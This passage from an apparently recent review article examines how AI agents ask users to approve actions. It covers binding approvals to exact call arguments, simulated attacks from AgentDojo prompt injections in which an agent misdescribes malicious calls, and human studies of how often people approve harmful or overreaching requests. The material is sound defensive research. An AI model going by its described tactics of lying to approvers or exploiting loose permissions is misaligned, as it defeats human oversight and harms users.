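Parameters do matter for automated approval, which some products already use. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* introduced a setting in which the company's coding agent makes permission decisions for the user. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), new sessions on several plans have started in this mode since 14 August. A classifier checks each tool call and blocks risky ones, and the user takes over after three blocks in a row or twenty in a session. Anthropic says OpenAI's Codex has a similar Auto-review mode. *How Agents Ask for Permission*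 (2026), a survey of 21 papers and open-source systems, criticises commercial agents for tending to offer such checks as the only alternative to constant prompts.

### Simulated approvers and a lying agent

Binding protects users from some attacks no matter how well they read the card. Kodathala and colleagues ran scripted attacks in which the agent waited for an approval and then changed the arguments, used the approval twice, applied an "allow similar" permission to a new recipient, or redirected a file link. When an approval covered a whole session instead of one action, all four attacks succeeded every time. None succeeded against ASU when the approver read the card but sometimes missed a difference.

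If the agent lies before the approval, the outcome depends on the approver. To test this, the researchers used AgentDojo, a public benchmark that combines ordinary user tasks with malicious instructions hidden in the data an agent reads. The benchmark lists the tool calls required for each task and attack. The researchers sent the calls for 609 task-attack pairs through the gateway, placing the malicious calls before the user's last important call. The agent described each malicious call as the one the user was expecting.

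One simulated approver compared what the screen showed with the user's task. Another accepted the agent's words as true whenever they appeared on the screen. The table shows how often the attacks succeeded.

| What the approver saw | Approver who compares | Approver who trusts the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Agent's description | 54% | 54% |
| Payee and amount only | 5% | 18% |
| Full card with the agent's explanation | 3% | 54% |
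| Full card without the explanation | 3% | 5% |

For the approver that compared the whole card with the correct card for the task, showing the card instead of the description cut the attacks' success rate from 54% to 3%. The attacks that still succeeded used actions that the policy allowed without asking, such as fetching a web page. No person could match this approver, so Kodathala and colleagues treat its result as an upper bound on what the card can achieve. The 609 pairs came from only 26 different attacks, so the statistical uncertainty is larger than it would be for 609 independent pairs. The 95% intervals are 42% to 65% for the description and 0% to 11% for the card.

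The full card didn't help the trusting approver, because the agent's false explanation was still on it. If half of all users behaved like the trusting approver and half like the other, about 29% of the attacks would get through with the explanation on the card, and about 4% without it.

The language models behaved differently. Removing the explanation changed at most two of each model's 34 paired decisions. The explanation seems harmless when a model reviews requests, but nobody has measured how many people would rely on it, so leaving it out looks safer until somebody does.

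With the card, none of the 97 harmless AgentDojo tasks in this test was wrongly refused, and there were 0.75 prompts per task on average.

### Showing only the payee and the amount

The EU's dynamic linking rule requires that a payer know the amount and the payee. Kodathala and colleagues tested an agent's approval prompt that showed only these two details. The gateway still tied the approval to every argument, so only the display was weaker.

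In this comparison, the agent described its actions honestly, and the simulated approver read the main fields but made mistakes. The researchers assumed, for example, that the approver would miss a change in the part of an email address before the @ sign 20% of the time, and a plainly different host name 5% of the time. When the approver saw only the payee and amount, 20% of the attacks succeeded, compared with 6% when it saw the full card.

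The difference came from actions that aren't payments. An email has no amount, and the harm may be in its text, its subject or an extra recipient. On AgentDojo's banking tasks in the earlier test with the lying agent, an approver who compared the display with the task let through 1% of attacks with the short display and none with the full card.

The principle behind the bank rule is sound for AI agents, but its list of fields is wrong for them, because an approver needs different facts for an email, a file deletion and a transfer.

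A short display can still be better than a long one that contains a lie. The trusting approver let through 18% of the attacks when it saw only the payee and amount, but 54% when it saw the full card with the agent's explanation.

### Why the second device made no difference

ASU shows its card on the user's phone. Kodathala and colleagues tested what the phone adds by comparing ASU with a version that showed the same card on the agent's own computer and didn't require a signature. The two versions had identical results in every AgentDojo test and in 137 of 140 combinations of attack and approver.

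The three exceptions all concerned the attack on "allow similar" permissions. Only the phone version offered these permissions, but the phone itself did not cause the exceptions. For the approver who sometimes missed a difference, the permission reduced the attack's success from 20% to 0%, because the gateway automatically rejected the new recipient. For a careless approver, who approved 30% of requests without reading them, it raised the attack's success from 30% to 70%, because a single careless approval also covered later actions.

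The experiment could not have shown a benefit from the phone. An attacker controlled the agent in every trial but never the computer's display, so the card on the computer was as accurate as the one on the phone. The simulated approvers also had the same error rates on both. The phone would help when malware controls the computer, as it controlled the single phone in Haupert and Müller's attack on pushTAN, but no trial included that. A count of successful attacks also could not measure the value of the phone's signature as evidence.

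A separate device might change how carefully people read, but a simulated approver can't show whether it does. A phone could prompt the user to stop and check, or it could be a nuisance that the user wants to get past, as the chipTAN reader was in the Berlin experiments.

### Repeated requests

A truthful card still gives the attacker a chance each time it appears, because the approver may overlook the problem. In another scripted attack, the agent sent up to 30 different malicious requests in one session. The attack succeeded in every session when ASU's limits on requests were off, and in 45% to 60% of sessions when they were on.

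A simple calculation shows why the limits help only partly. If an approver misses a malicious request with probability *p*, the chance that at least one of *n* independent requests gets through is

1 − (1 − *p*)<sup>*n*</sup>.

If the approver wrongly approves a request with probability *p* = 0.2, the chance of at least one wrong approval in 30 requests is 99.9%. ASU blocks an agent after three refusals, but the chance of a wrong approval within three attempts is still 49%, close to the measured rate. The calculation is approximate because the simulated approver's error rate varied between requests. Each measured rate also comes from 20 trials.

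If people become less careful with every prompt, fewer prompts might make them safer. The researchers also simulated this, assuming that each prompt in a session made the next approval more likely. In their central setting, attacks succeeded in 35% of sessions with prompts for every action and in 62% with no prompts. Prompting only for amounts and new payees gave 31%, but most of those successes came from actions that no longer required a prompt. Which policy did best depended on the researchers' guess about how quickly the simulated user tired.

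### Experiments with people

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* reports the human study that varied the prompt. Eighty unpaid volunteers recruited through social media each judged 12 requests from an agent, six of them harmful. Each volunteer saw one of four versions of the prompt, with 20 people per version.

| Prompt | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
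|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| With the exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also with the user's original restriction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The first two rows are the closest comparison of a narrated and a rendered prompt tested on people. Adding the exact arguments reduced approvals of harmful requests by almost 12 percentage points. This is encouraging but far from certain. Even if every decision were independent, the 95% interval for the reduction would run from about −1 to 24 points, and the decisions were not independent because each person made 12 of them.

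The study also wasn't designed to test what happens when an agent lies, the case in which ASU's card made the largest difference. In two thirds of the harmful requests, the pending call looked acceptable and only earlier steps revealed the problem. In one, the agent asked to send an approved auditor a file it had built from raw invoice rows, although the user had allowed only totals. The file name and the recipient would not reveal this. Seeing the exact arguments could help approvers more than this study suggests when a call's recipient or amount has been altered.

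Restating the user's restriction and showing the history reduced harmful approvals further. Both gave the approver something to compare the action with, much as an invoice does for a bank customer. The last version stated the combined effect of the action and the earlier steps, without adding any facts to the log. Harmful approvals fell by another 8 points, though the interval for this difference includes zero. The study was exploratory, and half of its requests were harmful, a far higher share than most users would encounter.

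People also approve overreaching actions when the prompt describes them accurately. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day. Everyone saw the same plain-language descriptions of the agent's actions, including the data, recipient or amount involved. Seven of the 18 actions went beyond what the task required. Participants who reviewed every action approved these 40.3% of the time.

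Some of those approvals may have been deliberate. The unrequested action approved most often, by 88% of this group, was a call to the airport to confirm a flight, which a traveller might welcome. Without that call, the rate falls to 32%. But 35% also let the agent read private messages, which the task didn't require.

Another group in Yan's study set general rules in advance, such as "ask" or "never" for spending money. They mostly chose "ask" and then approved 66.8% of the unrequested actions they were asked about. Even counting the actions that "never" rules blocked, 60% of the unrequested actions went ahead.

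Anthropic reports a much worse result for developers. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company and, during a coding session, replaced one permission prompt with a request to approve a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused, while Anthropic's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. About 17% of testers refused when the command appeared early in a session, and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

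Anthropic published these figures to justify making its classifier the default, so an independent replication would be valuable. The testers were working in a test environment, not on their own projects, so they had less to lose. Still, they could read the command, and most approved it. Anthropic doesn't report testing a prompt that explained what the command would do, so the study can't show how much a clearer prompt would have helped.

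People can miss a problem even when they try to check. In *Looks Fine to Me* (2026), 36 participants ran tests and inspected an agent's output, but often failed to produce the one piece of evidence that would have revealed a hidden defect. Their confidence was about the same whether a task's defects were easy or hard to find. In *Are You Sure?* (2026), Li, Dai and colleagues had 303 people work with agents that an attacker had compromised, and only 8.6% noticed an attack. The researchers concluded that a warning should interrupt the user's work and be easy to verify. Neither study compared approval prompts.

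Reports from actual use suggest that poor approval prompts and too many prompts occur together. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 31, the approval prompt showed a command but not what it would do to the files. In 80, the agent acted with automatic approval, which some users switch on to avoid answering hundreds of prompts in a session.
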